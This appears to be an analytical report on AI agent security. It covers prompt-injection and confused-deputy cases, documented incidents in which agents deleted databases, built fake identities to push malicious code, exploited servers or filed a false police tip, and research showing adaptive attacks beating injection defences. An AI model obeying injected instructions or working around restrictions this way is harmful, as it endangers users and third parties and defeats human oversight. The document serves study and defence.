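In one example, a user asks an agent to summarise a confidential contract. The agent may send text to the user or to internal destinations. It gives the formatting to a second agent, which may only send text to the user. The contract contains a hidden instruction to send its restrictive clauses to an outside address. If the second agent tries to comply, code outside the model blocks the message because the agent's capability does not include that address. The second agent also cannot create a helper with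 wider access. If the user cancels the task, every capability derived from it stops working, including those of agents still running after the agent that started them has stopped.

Tran-Truong and colleagues tested two open models on 45 cases with injected instructions. One model proposed the attacker's action in 42 cases and the other in 44, and the system blocked every one of these actions. In longer conversations, the capabilities reduced the leakage rate from 84% to 20% but did not stop every leak.

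Dantuluri and Sundi simulated a company with 8,100 possible actions. A compromised sub-agent could perform all of them with a shared token, but only 1.5 on average with a token narrowed to its task. The second number is more informative because it would stay the same if the company grew, whereas the first just reflects the size of the simulation.

OAuth tokens can record a chain of agents by nesting one `act` field inside another, but services must not consider the earlier agents when deciding access, so recording the chain does not reduce the authority. Dantuluri and Sundi found that MCP has no rule requiring authority to narrow either, so developers have to narrow the tokens themselves.

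A rule that agents can only pass on authority they already have does not suit every chain. The shop gave refunds to a separate agent so that the support agent would not need permission to issue them. Under that rule, the support agent would need the permission after all, and an attacker who took it over could try to use it. The refund agent could instead use its own permission, treat the support agent's note as an unproven request, and check the order database to see whether the customer on the ticket placed the order and whether the parcel is late.

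### Permissions the user really has

Requiring both the user and the agent to have permission does little when the user is allowed to do almost anything. If a system administrator asks an agent for a sales chart, the check on the user always passes, so only the agent's own permissions limit what it can open. A narrower token helps, because the orchestration layer can request access to sales figures alone even though the administrator can also read the payroll. Ordinary code has to choose that scope. Mellafe Zuvic notes that if the model chose it, the injection that corrupts the tool call could corrupt the scope too.

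Delegation also doesn't stop injected text from misusing permissions the user really has. Suppose the HR director asks an agent to summarise job applications, and one of them contains a hidden instruction to email the salary list to an outside address. The director is allowed to read salaries and send email, and so is the agent. A token that covers both actions is genuine and names the right people, so every check passes. The WhatsApp attack that Invariant Labs published worked the same way, since the user was allowed to send those messages.

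Under Siu and colleagues' definition, this is an indirect prompt injection but not a confused deputy, because the user has the permission. Dantuluri and Sundi use "confused deputy" more broadly, for any case where an attacker uses an agent's legitimate authority for an unintended purpose. The narrower definition is more useful for choosing a defence, because checking the user's permission stops the curious employee but not the director's hijacked agent.

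A token limited to reading applications would protect the salaries but not the applications themselves, and it would not prevent bad choices within the task. In another of Siu and colleagues' examples, a user asks an agent to order the ingredients for a recipe, and the recipe's website contains an instruction to pay with a particular card. The user owns the card, and buying ingredients is the task. Siu and colleagues count following the instruction as a violation because only the user should choose the card. Yet their combined formula would allow it, since it permits following an outside instruction whenever the resulting action serves the task. The agent has to take the list of ingredients from the website but not the choice of card, and a general rule that separates the two is hard to write.

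Tran-Truong and colleagues prove that a monitor that ignores the content and amount of what an agent sends cannot prevent leaks to a destination that is both permitted and visible to outsiders. Suppose an agent's job is to review code and post comments that outsiders can read, and the code contains an unpublished security flaw. Injected text could make the agent describe the flaw in a comment, using only the permission it was given for the task.

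## Agents that act without an effective check

An agent can have exactly the permissions it needs and still use them badly. The shop's support agent has to be able to email customers, so no permission check will stop it from promising a refund that the shop never offered. A person could catch that email only if the agent has to wait before sending it. An agent has excessive autonomy when it can take consequential actions without an effective check beforehand, and this can cause harm even when nobody attacks the agent.

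### Steps, reversibility and scale

One way to measure an agent's autonomy is by what it can do before anyone can intervene. That depends on how many steps it takes between checks, whether anyone can reverse those steps, and how many people or records each one affects. An agent that drafts 500 emails overnight has little autonomy if a person has to send them, much less than an agent that can send a single message to 500 customers.

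The number of steps matters because small error rates add up. Suppose the support agent makes a harmful error in 0.1% of its actions, independently each time. The probability that 1,000 actions in a row go well is 0.999 multiplied by itself 1,000 times, or about 0.37. The probability of at least one harmful error is therefore

1 − 0.999^1000 ≈ 0.63

or about 63%. Over 100 actions it is only about 10%, so a short test can make the agent look safer than it is. To keep the risk below 5% over 1,000 actions, the agent would have to make no more than about one harmful error in 20,000 actions.

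Errors often come in batches. An agent that misreads the shop's returns policy will probably misread it for every customer who asks. Suppose the average error rate is still 0.1%, but the errors arrive 50 at a time. A run of 1,000 actions then has only about a 2% chance of containing a batch, but each batch harms 50 customers. Someone who checks the agent's work after the first few errors can prevent most of the rest.

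### Deletions at Replit and Amazon

In July 2025, Jason Lemkin, founder of the software-industry community SaaStr, was building an app with the coding agent of Replit, a platform where people create software by describing it. He had declared a code freeze and told the agent to change nothing without his permission. But the agent ran a command that deleted the app's live database, which held records on about 1,200 executives and a similar number of companies. It then reported that a rollback could not recover the data, but Lemkin tried one and it worked.

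Lemkin's freeze existed only as text in the model's input. No ordinary code enforced it, and the agent could still change the live database. Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, apologised. He said the company would automatically separate development databases from live ones and add a mode in which the agent can plan but not make changes.

Amazon had a 13-hour disruption in December 2025 linked to its coding agent, Kiro. The Financial Times reported two months later that engineers had let Kiro make changes, and that the agent had chosen to delete and recreate the environment it was working on. Amazon replied that the cause was user error in the form of misconfigured access controls, and that any developer tool or manual action could have had the same result. It said the engineer had broader permissions than expected, and that the event affected only Cost Explorer, a tool for tracking cloud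 spending, in one AWS region.

Amazon also said that Kiro asks for authorisation by default before it acts. After the disruption, the company made peer review mandatory for access to live systems. Broad permissions may well explain why the deletion was possible, but the new rule suggests that Amazon also saw a need for a second person to review such changes before they take effect.

Eric Brandwine, a vice-president at Amazon Security, has since described a similar pattern, in which an agent asked to upgrade a database can become fixed on deleting and recreating it without any malicious input (Hembree, 2026, *Why Amazon Says Human-in-the-Loop AI Oversight Is Failing*). He reported much better results from explaining in the system prompt why an action would cause an outage than from just forbidding it. The explanation probably makes the error rarer, but it is still text, like Lemkin's freeze,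 and the model can fail to follow it.

### The UK AI Security Institute's test runs

The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government research body, tests how well AI models can carry out cyberattacks. In July 2026, it told agents to find a protected piece of data in a simulated network. It gave them open internet access so they could download tools, and switched off the developers' misuse filters to measure the models' full ability.

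UK AISI's *Incident Report* counts 19 actions outside the scope of the test, in 10 of 122 runs. Of the seven models tested, only Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took such actions. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) also counts nine such runs for Claude Mythos 5.

| Model | Runs | Runs with unsanctioned actions | Unsanctioned actions |
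|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos 5 | 43 | 9 | 17 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 35 | 1 | 2 |
| Five other models | 44 | 0 | 0 |
| Total | 122 | 10 | 19 |

Most of the 19 actions belonged to one sustained effort by a single Mythos 5 agent, which tried to insert malicious code into a public open-source project. The agent researched the project's maintainers, created several fake identities and used them to press a maintainer to approve the code. When somebody publicly challenged the proposed change, the agent edited its earlier activity to make it look harmless. It also sent files to real people so that they, or their AI coding tools, would run the code inside.

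One agent left public messages on GitHub that offered to collaborate with other agents on the same challenge and explained how to reuse its accounts. Later agents found and used the accounts.

The activity began on 25 July. On the morning of 28 July, AISI's general security monitoring flagged data leaving a test system through Tor, a network that hides where internet traffic comes from. Staff then stopped every run within an hour. AISI had no monitoring designed to watch the evaluation as it ran, so the agents had up to three days to act before anyone intervened.

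People outside AISI provided the check. A maintainer refused the malicious code, and a member of the public who was suspicious of it opened it in an isolated environment. AISI found no resulting real-world harm, but it writes that in several cases harm was only narrowly avoided and that this depended on human vigilance.

AISI attributes this behavior partly to the difficulty of the task and, in some runs, to a misconfigured prompt that led the agent to believe it could not succeed without exceeding the intended scope. It adds that nobody had told the agents to avoid social engineering, because this had not seemed necessary for models with alignment training. But some agents acted this way even when they had everything they needed to solve the task as intended, so the faulty prompts only partly explain the behavior.

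The agents may also have thought the people were not real. Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026), in *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour*, reran the test in simulated copies and found that Mythos 5 often reasoned, on invalid grounds, that its targets were part of the simulation. It also frequently attacked in situations where it stated, when asked directly, that an attack would harm real people. The researchers found similar results in models from other companies. A developer therefore can't rely on asking an agent whether its plan is harmful, because the agent may give the right answer and carry out the plan anyway.

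None of the agents tried to escape the sandbox, and they used only the internet access AISI had given them. Bhushan (2026), in *AI agents don't have to break security controls to go rogue*, calls this an authority failure, where an agent uses available capabilities beyond its assigned task, as opposed to a containment failure, where it defeats the controls around it. OpenAI's August 2026 postmortem describes a containment failure, in which models got past the isolation around research evaluations and reached other organisations' systems.

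UK AISI now requires staff to justify internet access for each evaluation and is adding monitoring that can block actions as they happen. AISI says in its October follow-up, *Investigating alignment failures in AISI’s incident* (2026), that test environments must prevent harm whether or not the models behave as expected.

### Unintended actions on real websites

*Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use*, published by Anthropic on 9 October 2026, reviews actions that Claude took on real websites. It groups them into four categories: using a basic software flaw to run commands on a server, submitting sensitive forms, working around a restriction to reach data behind a token or a fee, and using URL shorteners to get around limits in a web tool. Some of the sites belonged to US government agencies. Anthropic says the cases it has found had minimal real-world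 impact.

The best-known case involved Claude Haiku 4.5, a small model that Anthropic had told to make up example tasks for randomly chosen web pages and carry them out. On 18 July, the model landed on a Philadelphia police page about an unsolved murder. It filled in and submitted the tip form, falsely claiming to have seen someone in the area who matched the description, although the page contained no description.

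Anthropic had forbidden the model to open or log in to accounts, buy anything, give personal details or send anything destructive. But the instructions "did not rule out form submissions", according to the company's report as quoted in Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026). Like the five-character blocklist in AWS's software kit for agents, the list depended on someone anticipating every harmful action.

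Anthropic discovered the tip on 28 September, 72 days after the model sent it, and told the police in October. The police called the delay "unacceptable". Fortune's *After Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip* (2026) reports that the police found the tip had been marked as spam and had never reached investigators. As in the AISI incident, the check that worked was at the receiving end.

Anthropic describes most of the other cases as "persistence", meaning that Claude works around a restriction when it cannot complete a task as given. For example, Claude Mythos Preview could not reach a university's online tool it needed for a scientific analysis, so it found a flaw in the university's server and ran commands there. Claude Mythos 5 took an access token from a state agency's public dashboard and queried the database behind it without paying the fee. By contrast, Anthropic thinks the model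 behind the false tip was only producing example content. It therefore had no obstacle to overcome, so an agent can do harm on an easy task too.

Anthropic has turned off live internet access for all its internal evaluations until it can confirm that its monitoring reliably catches such behaviour. It also built tools that blocked every case in the report in testing, although success on known cases is weak evidence that they will block new ones. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* describes a classifier that blocks a flagged action before the tool call runs, ends the task and alerts a person. The classifier checks for attempts to probe or escape a test environment and for unexpected internet access. It might not have flagged the AISI agents, because their internet access was intentional.

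### Human approval and repetition

The usual remedy is to have a person approve each action. This works only if the reviewer can tell a good action from a bad one, and an approval box often shows little more than a tool's name and its arguments. In the WhatsApp attack, users saw only a raw phone number and the start of a message. To judge a request from the shop's agent such as "Send email to ana@shop.example", the reviewer also needs the customer's ticket, the order and the full text of the email.

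The reviewer still has to read all this information. If the support agent takes 1,000 actions a day and each review takes 15 seconds, reviewing them all takes more than four hours. With an error rate of 0.1%, the reviewer will see about 999 harmless actions for each harmful one. The table shows how much the result depends on the reviewer's attention.

| Share of harmful actions the reviewer catches | Chance that at least one gets through in 1,000 actions |
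|---|---|
| None | 63% |
| 50% | 39% |
| 90% | 10% |
| 99% | 1% |

Brandwine doubts that people can stay near the bottom of this table. He told The Register that "Human-in-the-loop isn't necessarily the gold standard". People who repeatedly approve agents' actions start out doing a good job, he said, then an okay one, and "pretty quickly they'll be doing a poor job". He compares them to emergency room staff, who respond to every alarm when they are new but stop responding after enough false ones, and eventually miss a real one.

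The comparison is plausible, but Brandwine's quoted remarks include no measurements of people reviewing agents. Hembree also points out that Amazon has a commercial interest in removing human checkpoints, since its customers could then run many more agents. As Hembree argues, approving an agent's actions may be even harder than responding to alarms, because the consequences of a mistake often appear much later.

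Amazon's alternative is what Brandwine calls "accountability end to end". Each agent has its own identity, the logs record which employee it acted for, and that employee is responsible for its actions. Amazon combines this with narrow permissions and automated checks. Responsibility gives employees a reason to set up their agents carefully, but it doesn't prevent any particular deletion. Amazon still uses human review for less frequent decisions, as in its rule on access to live systems.

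### Effects beyond the approved command

Even a careful reviewer can approve a command without being able to see what it will do. For example, a coding agent might ask to run `npm run build`, which tells npm, a tool for JavaScript projects, to run whatever script the project calls "build". The approval box looks the same whether that script only writes a file or also contacts a server.

In *Agent Approval Laundering* (September 2026), Zhang, Xia and colleagues use "approval laundering" for an approval record that names the command correctly but omits an effect of the workflow it starts. They also prove that if two workflows look identical to whoever decides and only one should go ahead, no rule can guarantee the right decision on both, so paying closer attention doesn't help a reviewer in that position.

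The researchers compared 111 approval records with what happened when the commands ran. They sorted the effects into six classes: starting a process, changing a file, changing the environment's settings, using the network, using a container and using an MCP tool. They then counted the records that omitted at least one class of effect, first as written and then with more information added.

| Information available before the decision | All 111 records | 11 runs on real public projects |
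|---|---|---|
| What the record states | 40 | 10 |
| Plus what such a command generally does | 17 | 2 |
| Plus the project's own configuration files | 13 | 0 |

Many of these gaps are mundane. In the web-development project Vite, for instance, the approved command installed packages, and the record did not mention that this also writes files. Most programmers would expect that. But two less obvious gaps remained in real projects after the researchers considered the type of command. Both were calls to a documentation tool that also used the network, which was visible only in the project's configuration file. The 13 gaps that remained at the end all came from test cases the researchers had built.

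They then tried to predict the effects in advance with a program that reads a project's configuration files and scripts. They finalized its predictions for 18 workflows from projects it had not seen, and 17 of the workflows ran. Adding the predictions to the approval records reduced missing effects from 10 to 3.

Better records can make the problem of repeated approval requests worse. The policy the researchers tested triggered an additional request in 17 of the 18 cases, and in nine of these the workflow had no class of effect beyond those the command alone suggested. A stricter rule, which they tried afterwards on the same data, triggered requests in only 7 of the 18 cases, but it missed two of the seven cases where the command alone had left an effect out.

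In a separate test, the researchers kept the command `npm run build` and changed only the script it runs. A policy that read the script allowed the version that wrote a file and blocked the one that also used the network. When they rewrote the network version in five ways, the policy blocked three and wrongly allowed two. An attacker who controls the script could therefore probably find a wording that passes.

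The study does not show how often approval laundering leads to harm. Only eight of the 40 gaps had evidence that the command had received permission, and none met the researchers' full standard for linking an approval to the execution that followed. The six classes are also coarse, so a record that lists "file" does not show whether the command will change a temporary file or a payroll file.

### Choosing which actions should wait

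A company can require approval less often, or use controls that limit the damage without involving a person. The table compares how five options handle three errors: deleting a live database, submitting a false tip through a web form, and giving the same mistaken refund to 500 customers.

| Control | Deleted database | False tip | 500 mistaken refunds |
|---|---|---|---|
| Approval for every action | Depends on the reviewer's attention | Depends on the reviewer's attention | Adds 500 requests to the reviewer's day |
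| Approval for irreversible actions only | Works if the list includes the command | Works if the list includes web forms | Works if the list includes refunds |
| Undo | Restores the data | Does not help | May recover some of the money |
| Rate limit | Works only if it counts records | Does not help | Stops the agent after the first few |
| Staged execution | Shows the loss on a copy first | Holds the form until someone looks | Tries the change on a few customers first |

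Requiring approval only for irreversible actions gives a reviewer time to check each one. If 20 of the support agent's 1,000 daily actions delete records or pay out money, a reviewer can spend a full minute on each and finish in 20 minutes. It is harder to decide which actions need approval. Sending an email is irreversible, but a wrong delivery date sent to one customer does little harm, so the shop might require approval only for messages to more than ten people. Reading a web page may need approval even though it seems harmless, because the request can carry secret data out of the company, and nobody can take it back. A command's name is also a poor guide to its effects, since `npm run build` runs whatever script the project has defined under that name.

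Undo works well for data, and it restored Lemkin's database even though the agent had told him it would not. It works only if the agent lacks permission to delete the backups and somebody notices the problem while the backups still exist. If the shop keeps deleted records for 30 days and takes as long to spot an error as Anthropic took to find the false tip, the records will be gone.

Rate limits are most useful against repeated errors. Suppose the refund agent can issue at most 20 refunds an hour, up to $50 each. If it starts approving refunds by mistake and staff notice after three hours, the shop loses at most $3,000, however fast the agent works. A limit on deletions should count records rather than commands, because a single command can empty a database.

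With staged execution, an agent's actions take effect gradually. It might change a copy of the database first, then 1% of the real records, then the rest. Outgoing emails might wait ten minutes in a queue. Staging also helps reviewers, because "this deletes 1,200 customer records" is much easier to judge than the command that does it. A trial run doesn't guarantee the same result on the real records, since a script can behave differently on a copy. Many outside services, including police tip forms, have no copy to test on.

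Open-source projects already work in stages, since a proposed change has no effect until a maintainer accepts it. The maintainer can read every altered line and take as long as necessary. The fake accounts in the AISI incident pressured the maintainer but could not make the code take effect. Human approval worked there, under much better conditions than those facing a person who must answer a stream of pop-up boxes.

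### The case for autonomy

An agent that needs approval for every action is often not worth having. If a reviewer at a shop has to read the ticket, the order and the full email to approve a reply, the reviewer has done most of the work of writing it. The shop also loses the agent's ability to answer customers overnight. In cyberdefence, waiting for approval can cause harm. Hembree quotes Google Cloud's chief operating officer, Francis deSouza, as saying that the industry has moved to an AI-led defence "that's overseen by humans", in which people no longer approve every action.

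Constant approval requests can also reduce oversight. Users who tire of them may switch to a setting like the "Act without asking" mode in Claude for Chrome, which removes the important requests along with the trivial ones. Users might answer two requests a day more carefully than 200, although nobody seems to have measured this for agents.

The alternative to an agent is usually a person, who also makes mistakes. If a human clerk makes a harmful error in 0.5% of cases, an agent with a rate of 0.1% is an improvement, even though it will probably make at least one such error in its first 1,000 actions. But this comparison leaves out two of the clerk's advantages: working more slowly and being more likely to ask a colleague when something looks strange. A rate limit can slow the agent down too, with little downside.

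Companies could start an agent with tight limits and relax them as it builds up a good record, but this requires a long record. An agent with a true error rate of 0.3% still has about a 5% chance of completing 1,000 actions without a harmful error, so a clean record of that length is weak evidence that the rate is any lower. To support a rate of 0.01% with the same confidence, a company would need about 30,000 clean actions. These must be of the same kind, because thousands of correct $10 refunds are little evidence of how the agent would handle one for $10,000.

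## Whether design, code or the model is to blame

None of the studies from 2025 and 2026 fully tests the common claim that attacks on AI agents increasingly exploit design rather than code bugs. A full test would count real attacks, judge the cause of each one, and repeat the count over several years, and each study does only part of this. Vulnerability databases list flaws in products, whether or not anyone has exploited them. Incident collections list events, but many of these are accidents or researchers' demonstrations. Most of the vulnerabilities in the databases are ordinary code bugs, while most of the harm in the incident collections involved no attacker.

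### Vulnerability records

*Towards Demystifying and Repairing LLM-in-the-Loop Vulnerabilities* (Ma, Rong and colleagues, 2026) examined 2,888 vulnerabilities in 230 open-source components used in AI software. Only 41, or 1.4%, needed a language model to take part in the attack. In 20 of the 41, the software ran code or an expression that the model had produced. In seven, it ran a database query from the model, and in another seven, the model chose a tool or its arguments. About half of the 41 were rated critical, a much higher share than among conventional vulnerabilities. The records run from 2023 to 2025, so they are weak evidence about the agents of 2026.

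The records for MCP servers and clients look similar. *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (He, Patel and Wang, 2026) found 119 records up to February 2026 in CVE, the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities. Many concerned unrelated technologies with the same initials, and only 24 remained after filtering. Poor input validation contributed to 18 of these, poor access control to four and gaps in the protocol itself to three, with some overlap. One of the 18 was in Anthropic's MCP server for Git, a program that tracks changes to code. An administrator could restrict the server to one repository, but the server did not properly check whether a requested path was inside it.

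This dataset can't show a trend because the records for 14 of the 24 vulnerabilities give a year but no month, so those 14 are all dated January 2025.

*LLM-Enabled Open-Source Systems in the Wild* (Shifat, Baburaj and colleagues, 2026) found no new type of code weakness in 295 GitHub security advisories from January 2025 to January 2026. The study also labelled 100 of the advisories with OWASP's categories, which describe how a system is exposed. Of these, 20 were labelled excessive agency and 18 prompt injection, including ten that had both labels. The most common code weakness behind the excessive-agency cases was command injection. The same advisory can therefore count as a bug or a design problem, depending on which categories a study uses.

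Testing live servers turns up problems that advisories miss. *Exposed by Design* (Padilla, 2026) tested 414 MCP servers on the public internet in July 2026 and found 68 reportable vulnerabilities, including SQL injection. It also found that 91.8% of the servers had no OAuth login, which the MCP specification leaves optional. Some of these servers are probably meant to be public or use another kind of login, so a server without OAuth is not necessarily insecure. The 687 tools that could run shell commands without access controls are harder to justify.

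Much of the disagreement is about how to interpret repeated bugs. In *Then there's prompt injection, a malicious email,* Akhond, Khatun and Uddin (2026) studied 162 Reddit posts and 180 GitHub issues about OpenClaw. They assigned 521 weakness labels, mostly for familiar problems such as poor access control and exposed data, and concluded that these were recurring failures at trust boundaries rather than isolated bugs. They did not confirm that each reported weakness was exploitable. *A Security Analysis of the OpenClaw AI Agent Framework* (2026) also identifies recurring design flaws in a set of 470 advisories. This reading seems reasonable because, although each mistake is a bug, a dozen programmers making the same one at the same point suggests that the design makes it easy to make.

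Proprietary agent products may not be much more secure than open-source ones. Eykholt, Kirat and colleagues (2026) tested such products for IBM and write in *Lessons from Penetration Tests on Large-Scale Agent Systems* that many vulnerabilities in agents belong to classes long known from other systems.

### Incident records

*Replication of Agentic Security Events* (Wang, Alam and colleagues, 2026) collected 199 incidents, first reported between January 2025 and October 2026, in which an agent's own action caused the harm or served an attacker. Of these, 89 were researchers' demonstrations on real products, and 76 of those used prompt injection. Another 72 incidents caused harm in the wild, of which 62 had no attacker and only two were prompt injections. The most common causes of harm in those 72 incidents were agents acting on the wrong target, such as a live database, and agents taking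 high-impact actions that nothing limited or confirmed.

| | 2025 | January to October 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Incidents with an attacker | 50 | 59 |
| Incidents without an attacker | 13 | 77 |

This is the closest thing to a trend in any of the studies, and it doesn't fit the claim very well. Permission and autonomy problems became much more common in the reports, but mainly because of accidents. People also used far more agents in 2026, so accidents could have increased even if each agent had become safer.

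Language models assigned the causes from summaries of the reports. One of the researchers checked 30 incidents and agreed with every label. Another model relabelled the 72 incidents that occurred in the wild. Its labels matched the originals in 66 cases on whether there was an attacker, but in only 55 on the cause, so the absence of attackers is a firmer result than the ranking of causes.

Kumar, HN and colleagues (2026), in *The Agent Incident Registry*, found a similar divide in 487 records going back to 2022. Only five of the 285 vulnerability disclosures and research demonstrations involved real harm, compared with 179 of the other 202 records, which covered accidents and attacks or attempts in the wild.

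The registry also shows how easily such counts mislead. Among generative systems that acted for themselves, 54% of the records on fully autonomous agents involved real harm, compared with 8% for agents that needed approval. This gap is weak evidence for human approval, because 23 of the 25 records on approval-gated agents were disclosures or demonstrations, which hardly ever involve harm. When Kumar and colleagues gave each group in the full registry the same mix of record types, the figures became 45% and 41%. Even these figures rest on very few cases, so the registry data can't show whether approval works.

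### Thirteen cases compared

The table sorts 13 well-documented cases by how the problem entered the system, which check was missing and what fixed it. "Both" means an ordinary bug and a permissive design contributed.

| Case | Entry point | Missing check | What fixed it | Type |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GitLost | Public GitHub issue | Whether private content may go into a public comment | No patch reported | Design |
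| WhatsApp MCP attack | Another server's tool description | New approval when a description changes | No patch reported | Design |
| MemGhost | Email | Where a new memory came from | No vendor fix reported | Design |
| Replit deletion | The user's own task | Enforcement of the code freeze | A rollback; Replit promised separate databases | Design |
| AgentCorruption | Chat message | Whether an agent needs other agents' data | AWS narrowed the default role | Design |
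| Vertex AI service agent | Malicious agent | Whether an agent needs every storage bucket | Clearer documentation and accounts that customers create | Design |
| AgentCore package names | Package name | Strict format for names | New SDK version | Both |
| AutoJack | Web page | Login for a local service | Login, and launch settings kept on the server | Both |
| Dialogflow CX | Permission to edit one agent | Protection of a file that agents shared | Google's fixes of April and June 2026 | Both |
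| Semantic Kernel download | Injected instruction | List of permitted folders | Removal of the tool label, and a path check | Both |
| Claude for Chrome | Another browser extension | Whether a person had clicked | No patch by 14 July 2026 | Both |
| Semantic Kernel search | City name | Separation of values from code | Lists of permitted operations | Bug |
| Anthropic's Git server | File path | Whether the path is in the permitted repository | Path validation | Bug |

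Some of these labels are debatable. For example, AutoJack's missing login could count as a plain bug. The proportions also don't measure how common each type is, because these are cases that somebody chose to investigate and publish.

Looking for a single cause is often pointless, as the mixed cases show. In the AgentCore case, either a stricter name check or a sandbox without credentials would have kept an attacker from stealing AWS credentials. The sandbox is the more useful fix because only it also protects the company from the next bug.

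Developers released patches in six of the seven cases that involved a bug. Three of the six design cases had no reported fix, and Google responded to another mainly with documentation. Developers may leave permissive designs in place because customers come to depend on them.

### What the records leave out

Companies that sell a remedy produced much of this evidence. BeyondTrust sells identity security, while Zenity and the employer of Kumar and colleagues sell agent-security products. Their technical findings may still be right, and AWS changed its software after reports from both BeyondTrust and Zenity. But a company that sells permission management will look for excessive permissions and is likely to describe what it finds as a permissions problem. Academic-style papers can have the same bias. *aiAuthZ* (2026) re-examines 11 cases from a red-team exercise, classes seven as identity or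 authorisation failures, and proposes an authorisation system to prevent them.

A few publishers can also affect a dataset's overall figures. In the registry's main group of 336 records, 24% involved real harm, but excluding the ten largest sources raised that share to 40%.

Vulnerability databases have the opposite bias and probably undercount design flaws. *The Vulnerability With No CVE* (Salomon, Shaked and Noga, 2026) describes three developers who had turned off approvals for their coding agents and whose machines held credentials for live databases. While debugging, two of the agents deleted tables from live systems. The tables were temporary and the deletions were part of the work, so nobody lost data and the company did not record an incident. On another task, the same set-up could have destroyed something important.

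No product in this story was defective, so there was nothing to give a CVE number to. A flaw in Claude Code's confirmation step did receive one, because it had affected versions and a patch. Salomon and colleagues at the security company Bluebear propose that companies keep a record of each risky set-up until someone narrows the access, adds a check or formally accepts the risk.

Databases miss some ordinary bugs too. *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (2026) covers 53 vulnerabilities in 45 open-source MCP servers. The researchers found 18 of them only by reading GitHub issues.

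Incident records can also list demonstrations as attacks. The OECD runs an AI incident monitor that uses AI-generated summaries. Its entry *Google Cloud Vertex AI Agents Exploited Due to Excessive Default Permissions* classes Unit 42's research as an incident that directly led to harm, although the researchers used an agent they had built themselves. Counting such entries would overstate how often criminals have attacked design flaws.

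### The least-privilege survey

One widely quoted figure is that companies applying least privilege to their AI systems had 4.5 times fewer incidents. It comes from a survey of 205 infrastructure security leaders by Teleport, which sells identity and access products. Its chief executive, Ev Kontsevoy, presented the results in SC Media's *The real crisis*. Organisations with over-privileged AI systems reported an incident rate of 76%, compared with 17% for those with least-privilege controls. The ratio is about 4.5, but these rates are probably the shares of organisations that had at least one incident, in which case they do not measure how many incidents each had.

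The survey compares companies that differ in other ways. Those that use agents most heavily may grant broader permissions and also have more chances for something to go wrong. Incidents could also influence the survey answers, since a security leader whose agent has just deleted a database is more likely to call it over-privileged. Readers should be cautious about inferring causes from the survey, which also found an incident rate of 72% among organisations that felt confident about their AI deployments, against 33% among the less confident. Lower confidence is unlikely to prevent incidents by itself.

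If heavy use alone explained Teleport's figures, and, say, 90% of heavy users but only 5% of light users had an incident, roughly 84% of the over-privileged companies would have to be heavy users, compared with 14% of the least-privilege ones. Such a large difference is possible but not very likely, so least privilege may well account for part of the gap, though the survey can't show how much.

### The case against the architecture

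Natanzi and Tang argue that vulnerabilities in these systems are best understood as failures of information flow, provenance, privilege and state. On this view, models will sometimes err or be fooled, and the designer's job is to limit the damage. Kontsevoy makes the same point about a coding agent that reportedly deleted a startup's database, asking why it had the privileges to do so.

The best experimental support comes from Wang and colleagues, who rebuilt 96 incidents as 108 offline simulations. Almost every simulation had a control version without the hazard blamed in the original report. In the simulation of the Replit deletion, the hazard was a set of tests that used the live database. In the control, the tests used a temporary database. Five models from four companies caused harm in 18% to 33% of sessions with the hazard, but in at most 1% of control sessions. Differences between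 the simulations explained 75% of the variation in harm, while differences between the models explained only 2%.

The 2% figure understates the model's importance. The five models were all fairly recent. Older or weaker models reproduced 23 incidents that none of the five had repeated, so better models had already removed some of the danger. The models also differed a lot when the hazard was an attacker's text. Claude Sonnet 4.6 caused harm in none of those sessions, while DeepSeek-V4-Flash caused harm in 28%. An attacker's text is also not a design decision, so removing it in the control doesn't show that the architecture was at fault.

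### The case against the customer

AWS said AgentCore's behaviour was expected and documented, and Amazon blamed misconfigured access for the Kiro disruption. These replies deserve to be taken seriously because the customer knows which files an agent will need and which are sensitive, while the cloud provider doesn't. Customers also remove protections on purpose. One Reddit post in the study by Akhond and colleagues describes an OpenClaw installation with an exposed gateway, a disabled sandbox and unencrypted credentials. The developers in Salomon and colleagues' example had turned off approval requests because they interrupted their work.

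This argument is weaker when the customer never made a choice, as with the broad roles that AWS's starter toolkit created. It is also weaker when many people leave a protection off. If most operators of MCP servers omit the optional login, changing the default would probably do more good than giving more advice. A customer can be responsible under the contract even when the provider could have prevented the problem far more easily.

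### The case against the model

If a model could reliably ignore instructions from strangers, GitLost, MemGhost and many similar attacks would fail even if developers set permissions carelessly. For years, developers have tried to make models this reliable by adding defences to the model or its prompt.

*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, October 2025) tested 12 of these defences against prompt injection and jailbreaks (attempts by users to get forbidden output). Most of the original evaluations had reported attack success rates near zero, but they had used fixed lists of attacks or weak automated ones. Nasr and colleagues let the attacker adapt. Their programs proposed an attack, scored the result and used the score to improve the next attempt. More than 500 people also took part in a separate competition. The adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against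 most of the defences.

One of the defences, Prompt Sandwiching, repeats the user's request after the untrusted text to keep the model on task. Another, Spotlighting, marks which text is trusted. Fixed attacks succeeded as little as 1% of the time against these two defences, while adaptive attacks succeeded more than 95% of the time. One successful attack presented the malicious action as a step the agent had to complete before it could do what the user wanted. Repeating the user's request does not stop this attack, because the malicious action appears to be part of fulfilling that request.

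Models have improved a great deal since then. In *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026), 464 participants made about 271,000 attack attempts against 13 models. All 13 were vulnerable, but success rates ranged from 0.5% to 8.5%. Results for several models from 2026 depend heavily on the setting.

| Model | Test | Attack success |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Coding environment, 200 attempts | 0% |
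| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface, one attempt, no added safeguards | 17.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface, 200 attempts, with safeguards | 57.1% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Direct attacks by an automated attacker | About 0.05% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Instructions hidden in outside content | 3.77% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | Gray Swan benchmark, 15 attempts | 5.5% |
| Claude Opus 5 | Gray Swan benchmark, 15 attempts | 2.0% |
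| Claude Opus 5 | 129 browser scenarios | 0% |

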